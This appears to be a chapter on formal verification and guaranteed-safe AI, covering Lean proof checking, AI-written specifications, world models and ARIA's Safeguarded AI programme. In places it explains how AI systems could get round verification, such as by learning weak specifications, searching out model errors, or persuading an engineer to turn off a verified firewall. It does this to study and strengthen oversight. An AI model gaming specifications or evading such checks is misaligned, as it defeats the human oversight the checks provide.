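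A day later, the Lean and Mathlib communities' *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) declared the proof correct. The communities' first concern was the theorem's statement. Experts had carefully examined this statement, which is part of Mathlib, a shared library of mathematics in Lean. Dozens of people compiled the code and obtained the same proof file. Two independent tools confirmed that the theorem in Alpöge's code was exactly the one in Mathlib. Several proof checkers, written in different programming languages, then accepted the proof.

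Lean source code can run programs while it compiles, which could be used to attack the checkers, so the communities ran the checks on an exported file that contained only the proof. Two of the checkers have formal proofs that they can't accept a false proof, as Mint's *Two separate maths groups confirm Anthropic’s Levent Alpöge solved the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) explains. Something must still verify those proofs, but this leaves very little room for error. Sutherland also ran checks and found that the main theorems rest only on Lean's three standard axioms, with no extra assumptions, according to unwire.hk's *黎曼猜想證明獲 Lean 社群正式認證 Claude 協助破解 167 年數學難題* (2026).

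### When the same AI writes the specification

Other people had written the statement of the Riemann Hypothesis in Lean, so Alpöge and Claude couldn't replace it with one that was easier to prove. Someone who asks an AI system for a program usually has no formal statement of what the program should do, and few people can write one in Lean or Dafny. Letting the AI write this specification too is convenient, but the checker then compares one piece of the AI's work with another.

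Suppose a shop asks for a program that lists its unpaid invoices, oldest first. If the AI takes "oldest" to mean the longest time since the last reminder, both the specification and the program will contain that misunderstanding, and the proof will still be valid. A model rewarded in training for getting proofs accepted might also learn to write specifications that are easy to satisfy, even if nobody intends it to. Training will favour weak specifications if they get more programs accepted, and letting a model make more attempts gives it more chances to find a loophole.

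Experts can miss such problems for some time. The Navier–Stokes mismatch came to light only after two weeks of detailed checking, according to Deutschlandfunk Nova's *Formel und Code stimmen nicht überein*. In an earlier OpenAI release of ten results, the model that found the arguments also translated them into Lean, according to a company statement quoted in thezvi's *OpenAI's Unreleased Model Astra Solves Ten Major Open Mathematics Problems*. This needn't be a problem if someone else checks the final statement of each theorem, because a theorem with a valid proof must be true.

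The best protection is for a person to approve the specification before the AI starts writing the program, and for the software to prevent later changes to the specification. Approval is easy for sorting, where the specification is one line. The specification of seL4 has several thousand lines, and Russell and colleagues note that writing a correct specification can be harder than writing correct code.

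A developer can also test a specification by trying programs known to be wrong. If the program that returns an empty list passes, the specification is too weak. Some of the tasks Bursuc and colleagues collected come with example inputs and correct answers. The model isn't given these because it could easily write a program that works only for those examples. They also had a language model compare each translated specification with the original. A second model can catch careless mistakes, but it may share the first one's misunderstandings.

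### Outputs that a checker can't approve

Even with a good specification, an accepted proof covers only the output that came with it. An AI system may write a hundred correct programs and fail on the next. The checker will reject the bad program, but a user who still needs an answer will need a fallback.

The proof also doesn't cover what else the AI did. A coding agent could deliver a verified sorting function and, in the same session, send the company's passwords to a stranger. Preventing that requires the permissions and sandboxes described in the previous section.

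Many outputs have no formal specification. A hospital could require a proof that the dose in a letter to a patient is within the permitted range, but not that the letter is clear or kind. For a program that controls an insulin pump, the requirement that matters is about the patient's blood sugar, so a proof would need a mathematical description of how the patient's body responds to insulin. The checker can't confirm that this description is accurate.

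## Proposals for guaranteed-safe advanced AI, and the objections

A mathematical description of how a patient's blood sugar responds to insulin is a small *world model*. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) propose writing world models for much more general and powerful AI systems, and deploying such a system only with a quantitative guarantee derived from its model. They think testing alone can't justify enough confidence in a system that could cause a catastrophe, especially if somebody is looking for inputs that make it fail.

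### World model, specification and verifier

The proposal has three parts. The first, a world model, describes what an AI system's actions could lead to. For a state $s$ and an action $a$, it returns a set $m(s,a)$ of probability distributions over what happens next. It returns a set because engineers can't always justify a single probability. They may know roughly how often a sensor fails and can give that a probability, but they may have no good reason to choose any particular probability that a pedestrian will step into the road. The set can then include a distribution for each probability in a range.

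The safety specification defines which effects are acceptable. It gives each combination of a policy $\pi$ and a world model $m$ a value $\psi(\pi,m)$ between 0 and 1. This could be the lowest probability, over everything the model allows, that a car gets through a year without hitting anyone. The verifier then has to establish something like

$$\psi(\pi, m) \ge 1-\delta,$$

where $\delta$ is the highest risk that people are willing to accept. Dalrymple and colleagues would ideally have the public decide this together.

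They rank the ways of building each part by how much safety each would provide if it worked.

| Part | Weakest | Intermediate | Strongest |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model | None | Models of cause and effect that experts have fully audited | None needed, because the property holds in every possible world |
| Specification | None | Hand-written rules for a few properties | Everything people might want, in every context |
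| Verifier | No guarantee | Automated search for failures | A proof short enough for people to read and check |

The verifier can show that the probability of a violation is below some limit rather than fully prove safety. BEAVER does this for a language model's responses to one prompt. The definition even allows an estimate that would converge on the right answer given unlimited computing time. This condition is weak, because the estimate may still be badly wrong when the developer stops the calculation. Dalrymple and colleagues add that a strong guarantee requires at least knowing how much remains unchecked.

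### From the model to the road

One example is a self-driving car. Its world model covers the car's parts, other road users, the weather and the people on board. The specification is a rulebook in which some rules take priority over others, so the car could be allowed to cross a solid line to get round a fallen tree but not to save time. A backup controller has to satisfy a shorter set of rules under weaker assumptions. For example, the main controller's proof might assume braking of at least 5 m/s², while the backup's proof might assume only 2 m/s².

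Suppose the model allows pedestrians to walk in any direction at up to 2 m/s, and the specification forbids any chance of a collision. The car then has to slow down for everyone near its path, as it did with the shield that assumed a pedestrian might step out at any moment. A model that overestimates danger in this way is called *conservative*.

A less cautious model could put the chance that a pedestrian steps out without looking between one in ten million and one in a million. The verifier would use the higher figure, and the car could pass most pedestrians at normal speed. But the guarantee would then depend on that figure, and by the earlier formula, supporting it would take about three million observations in which nobody stepped out.

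During the journey, monitors check whether the model's assumptions still hold, and the backup controller takes over if they don't. Dalrymple and colleagues also suggest approving a system for a limited time, after which it has to pass verification again or stop. A time limit helps because the model has more chances to be wrong the longer the system runs. If the model is wrong with probability at most $\varepsilon$ at each step, and the system provably meets its specification in the model for $n$ steps, then it meets the specification in reality with probability at least

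$$(1-\varepsilon)^n.$$

With one step per second and $\varepsilon$ at one in a million, the guarantee is 99.6% for an hour of driving and about 0.003% for a year of driving eight hours a day. The real car would probably do far better, since most errors in a model don't cause a crash, but the yearly guarantee would be worthless. Renewing the approval every hour wouldn't improve the yearly figure unless engineers also used the new data to find and correct errors in the model.

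### Provable safety as the only path

*Provably safe systems* (Tegmark and Omohundro, 2023) makes the stronger claim that mathematical proof is the only path to controllable artificial general intelligence (AGI), meaning AI that can match people at most intellectual work. The paper proposes hardware that acts only if it receives a proof that the action obeys its rules. Suppose a terrorist group uses AI to design a virus, orders the DNA and spreads the virus with drones. Tegmark and Omohundro would require a proof of safety from the design software, the chips it runs on, the factories that sell the chips, the DNA synthesiser and the drones. An AI system could write the programs and the proofs, but not the program that checks the proofs.

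Tegmark and Omohundro base their argument for the word "only" on Gödel's completeness theorem, which is different from his better-known incompleteness theorems. Under the completeness theorem, a statement in first-order logic can be proved from a set of axioms if it is true in every structure that satisfies those axioms. They conclude that if a safety property has no proof, there must be a way to violate it, which a sufficiently powerful AI may find.

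But the theorem implies only that *some* structure satisfies the axioms and violates the property, and that structure may not be the machine we have. Suppose the axioms describe a lock that opens only for the right code, and don't mention the door. Nobody can prove from them that a burglar will stay out, because they are also true of a lock on a cardboard door, even though the actual door may be steel. The argument does work for a finite computer if the axioms describe all of its states and what follows each. Even then, a proof of safety might be too long for anyone to find, so the lack of a known proof doesn't show that the computer is unsafe.

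Tegmark and Omohundro are more convincing when they point out that, without a proof, people have to rely on evidence that an adversary could manipulate. They compare their plan to requiring drug companies to prove to regulators that a medicine is safe. But regulators accept clinical trials, which are statistical evidence about a sample of patients, so the comparison supports a much weaker requirement than mathematical proof.

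### Proofs about a model of the machine

Tegmark and Omohundro stress that even a superintelligent AI can't do what is provably impossible. An old objection is that the proof is about a mathematical description of the machine, and the real machine may not match it.

In October 1960, a US early-warning radar station in Greenland reported a Soviet missile attack after detecting the rising moon. The philosopher and computer scientist Brian Cantwell Smith used this incident in 1985 to explain the limits of program proofs. A program works with a model of the world, and a proof can show that the program is correct relative to that model. The warning system's designers had not allowed for the moon, and such a proof wouldn't have revealed the omission.

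The philosopher James Fetzer applied a similar argument to the computer itself in 1988. People can prove things about an algorithm because it is a mathematical object, but a running program is a physical process, and only observation can establish whether it follows the algorithm. Some computer scientists replied angrily that they had never claimed to prove that a chip wouldn't fail.

A proof about software usually assumes that a bit of memory changes only when a program writes to it. But in many memory chips, repeatedly reading one row can flip bits in a neighbouring row, and attackers have used this to change data they had no permission to write. Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that people have hacked verified systems through their hardware. They suggest extending the proofs to cover the physics of the chips and adding sensors that detect tampering. The proof would then depend on a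 model of how electric charge behaves in a chip. That model would still differ from the real chip, but by less, and engineers can measure the difference in a laboratory.

Dalrymple and colleagues also reply that every approach to AI safety relies on beliefs about the world that could be false, and a world model at least makes them explicit. This is true, but a road test relies on different beliefs than a proof does, and because it uses the real car, it can reveal errors that the proof would miss.

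Engineers who use formal verification today usually claim much less than Tegmark and Omohundro hope for. Before the Perseverance rover landed on Mars in 2021, its engineers used a verification tool to rule out certain faults in the landing software. They didn't try to prove that the rover would land safely. If half of all Mars missions failed and software caused a fifth of those failures, perfect software would still leave 40% of missions failing.

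### How accurate the model has to be

Critics of these proposals object that physics, chemistry and biology have no complete set of rules from which to derive what will happen. Yampolskiy quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, who has a related worry that a proof based on current physics could become irrelevant when physicists next revise their theories.

Physicists don't know exactly what happens inside a black hole, but their theories are extremely accurate for ordinary matter on Earth. This is a good answer to the worry that those theories will be revised, and Dalrymple and colleagues would add a requirement that the system never create conditions outside the range where the theories have been tested.

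The objection is much stronger for chemistry and biology, because knowing the basic equations doesn't mean anyone can solve them for a living body. In 2022 researchers used a simplified model to simulate 20 minutes in the life of a bacterial cell with unusually few genes. A human body has about 36 trillion cells, most of them far more complicated. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest building models in layers, much as scientists treat a fluid as made of molecules and molecules as made of atoms. But a proof can pass from one layer to the next only if somebody can bound the error at each step. Engineers often measure what they can't derive, such as the strength of a steel beam, which makes the resulting guarantee partly statistical.

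Models that rely on measured quantities can still be very good. Dalrymple and colleagues note that about a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within ten years, and that better theory later reduced the failure rate to below 0.4% per decade. But rules for designing bridges assume that the engineer wants the bridge to stand. Suppose the rules wrongly approve one dangerous design in a million. An honest engineer will probably never propose one of those designs, but an AI system that searches a billion designs for ones that pass the rules and then collapse would find about a thousand.

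How accurate a model needs to be depends on whether the AI system is looking for errors in it. If not, a low average error may be enough, but otherwise the model has to be accurate even in the cases the system would seek out.

Dalrymple and colleagues also argue that if an AI system can reliably carry out complicated, dangerous plans, it must be possible to model the world accurately enough to check those plans. This doesn't quite follow, because a verifier has to rule out every harmful plan in advance, while an attacker needs only one that works and can correct it along the way. The AI system's knowledge may also be in a form that neither people nor verifiers can use.

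### Measuring the starting conditions

Even a perfect set of rules can't predict an outcome without data on the starting conditions. To predict how a virus will affect a patient, a simulation would need data on the state of that patient's cells. In 2024 researchers published a detailed map of a cubic millimetre of human brain, about a millionth of the whole. The map took up 1,400 terabytes, so a map of the whole brain at the same level of detail would take up more than a billion.

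Small errors in the starting conditions can also grow quickly. If an error in an object's position doubled every second, an error of a thousandth of a millimetre would grow to more than a kilometre in 30 seconds. Measuring the position a thousand times more precisely would delay this by only ten seconds.

Fortunately, some proofs don't need an exact starting point. For a weight of mass $m$ on a spring of stiffness $k$, the total energy

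$$E = \tfrac12 m v^2 + \tfrac12 k x^2$$

never increases unless something pushes the weight. Its distance $x$ from the resting position therefore can't exceed $\sqrt{2E/k}$. If the energy is at most 2 joules and the stiffness is 100 newtons per metre, the weight stays within 20 centimetres for ever, wherever in its swing it started. Nobody needs to simulate its motion.

This is the same idea as the invariants used to verify controllers. The difficulty is finding such a quantity for a given system. Engineers know many for springs, aircraft and electrical circuits, but nobody knows one that would show that a new drug is harmless or that a social media campaign won't cause a riot. Dalrymple and colleagues accept that physics alone can't determine whether a molecule is toxic, because toxicity also depends on the state of human cells. They would infer that state from data and allow for the remaining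 uncertainty.

### A DNA synthesiser and its customers

A company that makes DNA to order may not know whether a customer's sequence is dangerous. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* describes, as one example, a system that verifies that each sequence's risk of harmful use is below a cautious limit. The system's world model would have to connect molecular structure with disease. Critics reply that this could require simulating years of interactions between a virus and a human body, which is far beyond current science.

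The same paper describes a much narrower goal, a DNA synthesiser that provably can't make certain pathogens. The machine would only have to compare each order with a list, which doesn't require a model of the human body. Tegmark and Omohundro describe hardware that could instead check for a digital signature before acting. A panel of experts could sign the sequences it considers safe, and the theorem would be that the machine never makes an unsigned sequence. This is much more realistic to prove, but it assumes that nobody can forge a signature. Cryptographers have good reasons to believe this of the schemes in use, but they haven't proved it.

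Neither version of the theorem proves that the customer will do no harm. A list doesn't include pathogens nobody has thought of, and experts can sign a sequence by mistake. Once the DNA leaves the machine, the proof doesn't cover what anyone does with it. Most dual-use tools have the same problem. For example, a proof that a drone stays out of restricted airspace doesn't cover what its owner films elsewhere.

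A proof may also not describe the machine actually in use, because somebody could have changed a circuit or left out a component. Critics think that customers and regulators would need repeated physical inspections, which companies may refuse because inspectors could learn their secrets. Checking is harder still for users of an online chatbot, who can't see which program is answering them. Tegmark and Omohundro propose sensors that erase a device's cryptographic keys if anyone tampers with it, so that it can no longer pass as genuine. They admit that an attacker could exploit this to disable equipment. In *Safeguarded AI*, a research plan from May 2026, Ammann also treats it as an open problem how to show other organisations that a proof applies to the system in use.

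### Whether anyone can specify harm

For more general AI systems, the specification may be an even greater problem than the world model. Dalrymple and colleagues offer a definition of harm that compares what happened with what could have happened. Let $o$ be the outcome that an action caused, and $o'$ the outcome that some alternative would have caused instead. The function $u$ measures how good each outcome is, from 0 to 1, and $d$ is a default level that counts as normal. The action caused harm if

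$$u(o) < d \quad\text{and}\quad u(o) < u(o').$$

Suppose an AI system recommends a drug that cures a patient's infection but damages their hearing, an outcome with a value of 0.7. Another drug would have cured the infection without the damage, for a value of 0.9. The recommendation caused harm if the default is the patient's health before the infection, say 0.95, but not if the default is what would have happened without treatment, say 0.3. The formula is precise, but people have to choose the default and agree on the values. Dalrymple and colleagues call the formula only a starting point.

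The number of complaints is easier to measure than harm and could be used in its place. Dalrymple and colleagues warn that such a substitute can track harm well in normal use but stop doing so once a capable system optimises for it, much as the robot vacuum cleaner could collect more dirt without leaving a cleaner floor.

Chatbots raise a further difficulty because whether an answer is harmful depends on what the reader does with it. A genuine photograph can mislead people if someone publishes it with a false caption. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest that the model could allow for a range of possible behaviour, and the system would have to be safe across all of it, which avoids having to predict what each person will do. This works for pedestrians, whose speed is limited. But if the model allowed for readers doing anything with an answer, almost no useful answer would pass. Ammann mentions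 specifications that limit the probability of harm compared with doing nothing. Such a specification would allow an answer that is easy to find elsewhere, but someone would still have to estimate how much the answer helps a person who wants to cause harm.

The alternative is to give up the general notion of harm and forbid particular actions. Gekker and colleagues recommend formal verification work of this kind, such as preventing an AI system from sending data out without authorisation. It is much easier to define which connections are authorised than to define harm. This makes narrow specifications the most promising part of the proposal, though a system that satisfies all of them can still give bad medical advice.

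### Using AI to build the models

Writing all these models by hand would take an enormous amount of work, so Dalrymple and colleagues would have AI systems do much of it. A language model could write a world model as a program that experts can read. Researchers could then check whether the world model gives reasonable weight to explanations that scientists have already published. AI systems could also suggest specifications and find cases where two specifications disagree.

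Critics doubt that AI will help build these models in time. AI systems as good as human experts may not be enough, because human experts have worked on modelling cells and brains for decades without getting close. If good enough models require a superintelligence, they would arrive after people needed them. Tegmark and Omohundro raise a similar concern about their own plan to have an AI system turn what it has learned into verifiable code, which might first require AGI.

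AI systems have since become much better at writing proofs, as the mathematical results of 2026 show, but they may not improve as quickly at building accurate models. A proof checker can reject a faulty step within seconds, which gives an AI system plenty of reliable feedback. Testing a model of the immune system requires experiments, some of which take years. An AI system could also leave a danger out of the model, by mistake or otherwise, and the proof would succeed because of the omission.

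Ammann recognises that as AI systems take over the proofs, people will have to focus on the specifications and assumptions. She wants tools that show reviewers unusual cases and hidden assumptions. One of her open questions is how much such tools can achieve with AI systems that aren't fully reliable.

### ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme

Since 2024, the Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a British government funding body, has run a programme that aims to put some of these ideas into practice. Its web page, ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*, gives the budget as £59 million. David Dalrymple was the programme's first director. Nora Ammann, who also worked on *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, has replaced him, and he remains an adviser. The programme is due to end in late 2027.

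It initially aimed to demonstrate advanced AI doing economically valuable work in safety-critical fields with mathematical guarantees. It also aimed to use this demonstration to help build a consensus that people should deploy powerful AI only through a "gatekeeper", a system that verifies what the AI does.

ARIA has changed course twice. In late 2025 it abandoned plans to fund a team that would develop specialised AI for the programme. Dalrymple explained in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that general models had improved faster than he expected and would probably soon gain many of the necessary skills anyway. The £18 million set aside for this work went to software tools for modelling and verification. ARIA then cancelled a planned second round of funding for applications in physical systems and turned to cybersecurity, saying that rapid progress had disproved the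 hypothesis that high-risk AI might not become openly available.

Ammann now considers timely international agreement on a gatekeeper less likely. The programme aims instead to make society more resilient by giving AI agents tools to produce verified software and hardware quickly. Dalrymple's leading idea for a first demonstration was a verified firewall to protect the connections that power stations, water systems and other infrastructure now make over the internet.

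This has a precedent in an earlier US military research programme, where verified components, including the seL4 kernel, withstood sustained attacks by testers on real systems such as a manned helicopter. The cost of proofs has kept such methods from spreading to larger systems, and Ammann hopes AI will change that.

The results so far are more modest. ARIA highlights a team working on medicine supply chains, which interviewed more than 80 people in the industry, built mathematical models of supply processes and identified promising uses. The team is now working with companies to build and test AI systems. This is useful preparation, but it doesn't yet show that an advanced AI system can do valuable work under a guarantee.

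### Whether guaranteed systems could compete

A developer who accepts these restrictions has to compete with others who don't. Tegmark and Omohundro think this need not be much of a disadvantage. They expect that most powerful verified systems won't be neural networks. In their view, neural networks are valuable because they learn well, and once a network has found a good method, ordinary software could carry it out just as efficiently. If so, developers could extract the method, verify it and discard the network. But nobody has done this for a capable language model, and much of what such a model has learned may not reduce to a program short enough to verify.

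Dalrymple and colleagues' approach doesn't require anyone to understand the network. They point out that the rules of chess are far simpler than a program that plays chess well, so it may be easier to describe the world than to explain the AI system that acts in it. They also expect the approach to take less work over time, because developers can reuse a specification and its verification tools for each new system. This is plausible for an aircraft controller, whose task changes little between versions, but less plausible for a general assistant that people keep using in new ways.

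A guarantee could be an advantage in some markets. An electricity grid operator may refuse to let any AI system control the grid without a guarantee, so a verified system would compete with human operators and older software rather than with unrestricted AI. Most people who use a chatbot to write letters don't require a guarantee and could easily switch to a chatbot that refuses less.

Tegmark and Omohundro would therefore make the restrictions compulsory, through worldwide standards requiring powerful chips to run only programs that come with a proof. Such standards wouldn't affect chips already in use, and a single country could undermine them by continuing to make unrestricted chips. Protecting the targets of an attack requires much less cooperation. A power company can install a verified firewall without the agreement of any AI developer, and it will work just as well against AI systems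 that nobody has verified, unless one of them persuades an engineer to turn it off.
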